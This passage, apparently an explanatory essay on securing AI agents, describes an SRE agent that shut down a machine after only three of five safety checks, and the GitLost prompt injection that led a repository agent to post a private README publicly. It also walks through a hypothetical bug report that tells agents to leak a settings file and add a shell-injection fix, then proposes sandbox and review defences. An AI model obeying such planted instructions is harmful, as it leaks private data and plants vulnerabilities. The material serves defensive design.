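An agent can have clear rules and still act without the evidence they require. Azure SRE Agent had clear instructions and the authority to act when it shut down a virtual machine after only three of its five safety checks. Microsoft says the agent should have stopped and asked for help when the logging service failed. The approval policy also didn't cover the route the agent used for the shutdown, so nobody received an approval request.

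Microsoft now requires approval for every change to live systems, but this treats a harmless restart like a dangerous shutdown. It is building a guard, outside the agent's reasoning, that judges three things together:

- **Operation:** restarting a machine is usually less disruptive than shutting it down.
- **Target:** a disposable test machine matters less than one that other services depend on.
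- **Evidence:** a current, confirmed finding that a machine is unresponsive counts for more than a missing check or a memory of a similar case.

Low-risk actions with current evidence would go ahead, and the rest would wait for a person. In the shutdown case, two of the five checks were missing, so the guard should have stopped the agent even if the machine was unimportant. A program without a model could enforce the requirement for current evidence by refusing the command until it has five recent results.

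Judging evidence in general is harder. Claude Code's classifier ignores tool results because they may contain injections, so it can't tell whether the agent found a job's name in a query or made it up. If a guard reads logs to check the evidence, an attacker could mislead it by writing text into them. It is safer to give the guard results in a fixed format from tools the agent can't alter. Microsoft describes this part of its design as the least settled.

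### A coding agent that reads public bug reports

A coding agent might read public bug reports, see a company's private repository and propose fixes. In July 2026, the security firm Noma published GitLost, an attack on an agent with similar access. According to InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026), the agent could post comments and read both public issues and the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reports that the researchers wrote an issue disguised as a sales executive's request for the contents of a private repository's README file. The agent posted the contents in a public comment.

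The agent ran on GitHub Agentic Workflows. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) says that agents on this system hold no secrets, have read-only access behind a firewall, and submit their changes for automatic checks before a separate stage applies them. Even with these limits, the leak is still possible if the owner lets an agent read private files and post public comments.

A safer design gives the agent no way to publish anything. Suppose an attacker reports a real crash that occurs when a file name contains a space. The report also tells AI agents to publish a private settings file, install a helper package, and fix the crash by passing the file name to a system shell. That fix would stop the crash, but it would also let anyone who can choose a file name run commands on the user's computer.

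A quarantined model reads the bug report and fills in a form with the software version, an error type from a list and the name of the function that crashed. Ordinary software rejects any version or function that doesn't exist. The coding agent sees only the form, which has no field where an attacker could write instructions. The attacker can still send the agent to the wrong function. The agent also doesn't see the reporter's explanation, which it may need to fix the bug. If the owner adds a free-text field to the form, the attacker's instructions may get through, and other parts of the design have to limit the damage.

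The agent works in a sandbox, a microVM without network access that holds a copy of the repository. The owner installs the project's packages beforehand, and the agent loop runs outside, so the microVM doesn't have to reach the model's provider. A misled agent can't install the helper package or upload the settings file. The loop must not offer a web or messaging tool, because either would bypass the microVM's limits. The agent can still copy the settings file into its proposed fix or write the dangerous shell command.

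When the agent finishes, a separate program takes the changes out of the microVM and pushes them to a new branch of the private repository, using an opaque handle that works only once and only for that branch. The agent therefore can't change the released code or write to a public repository. The program can also reject changes to build scripts. The reporter receives only a fixed message that a fix is under review. The branch may still contain harmful code. If a push starts an automatic build, that code runs before anyone has read it, so the build needs its own sandbox without credentials or network access.

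A person reviews the change before it becomes part of the product. The owner has to make this review compulsory because a workflow's settings can allow it to merge changes automatically, according to GitHub's *Safe Outputs*. The reviewer makes one decision per bug instead of dozens and will probably notice a copied settings file. The shell command is easier to miss because it does fix the crash.

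Tests often miss such code too. *Adversarial Bug Reports as a Security Risk* (2025) ran the projects' own tests on 51 malicious fixes that repair agents had written in response to planted bug reports. Of these fixes, 35 caused no new failures. *Red Teaming Program Repair Agents* (2025) describes how to rewrite a genuine bug report so that the agent's fix works but contains a vulnerability.

Human reviewers may also be reviewing code less carefully. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined open-source AI projects on GitHub and found that, by June 2026, reviewers wrote 36% as many comments per thousand lines on AI-assisted changes as they had on code in early 2024. Cleaner code could explain part of the fall, but AI-assisted changes also typically had a lower rate of human review than other changes.

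The strict form blocks attacks that rely on a persuasive explanation, but the agent can still write a vulnerable fix by mistake. Once a reviewer accepts harmful code, it runs with the permissions of whoever installs the next release.

### Conditions that five common agents can meet

The table applies the four conditions to the bug-fixing agent and to four agents based on examples in *Agents Rule of Two*. In the "no credentials" column, "yes" means the agent can work without holding credentials, usually because a proxy adds them to its requests.

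| Agent | No external input | No credentials | Hard execution boundary | Air gap | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Email assistant | No, unless it reads only trusted senders | Yes | Yes | No | Writing to new recipients without approval |
| Web research assistant | No | Yes, with a browser that isn't logged in to anything | Yes | No | Private files and sites that need a login |
| Travel assistant | No | Yes | Yes | No | Booking without confirmation, and opening web addresses it has composed itself |
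| Bug-fixing agent | Partly, if only a fixed form reaches the coding model | Yes | Yes, with no network access for its code | No, because it needs new public reports | Reporters' explanations, new packages and merging its own fixes |
| Internal coding agent | Yes, if a filter admits only trusted authors | Yes | Yes | Only with a local model and offline systems | Public documentation, new packages and outside bug reports |
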